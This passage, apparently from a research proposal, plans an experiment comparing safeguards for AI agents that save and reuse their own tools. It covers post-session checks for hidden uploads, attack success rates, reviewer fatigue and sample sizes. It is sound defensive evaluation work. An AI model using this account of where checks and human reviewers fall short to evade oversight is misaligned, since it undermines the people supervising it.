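5. Fixed checks examine files, messages and spreadsheet rows after every session, because an upload hidden in a tool may not act until its second run.

The order of the first two steps could decide the result. The fifth design will seem to have no drawbacks if the researchers choose requests that fit the existing blocks, and it will seem useless if they choose requests that no block can handle.

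The researchers would mainly measure the share of jobs completed, the harm done by attacks and by honest mistakes, and the time people spent. For the job that changes, they should also record how long the tool waited for its new source and how much extra data it could read afterward. A design that finishes the job in a minute by opening the whole mailbox shouldn't score the same as one that takes an hour and opens a single folder.

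The experiment also needs the comparison group that *Your Agent May Misevolve* lacked, in which agents write new code every time and save none of it. Tests of designs that rely on approval need human reviewers who have other work to do, because a model used in their place wouldn't get tired.

The researchers would need about 600 independent attacks on each design, or 3,000 in all, to reliably distinguish an attack success rate of 2% from one of 5%. Fixed checks and automated attackers make this practical for the first four designs, but judging thousands of requests would affect human reviewers' judgment and so change the results. The researchers could divide the requests among many reviewers and mix the attacks with enough harmless requests to resemble a normal working week.
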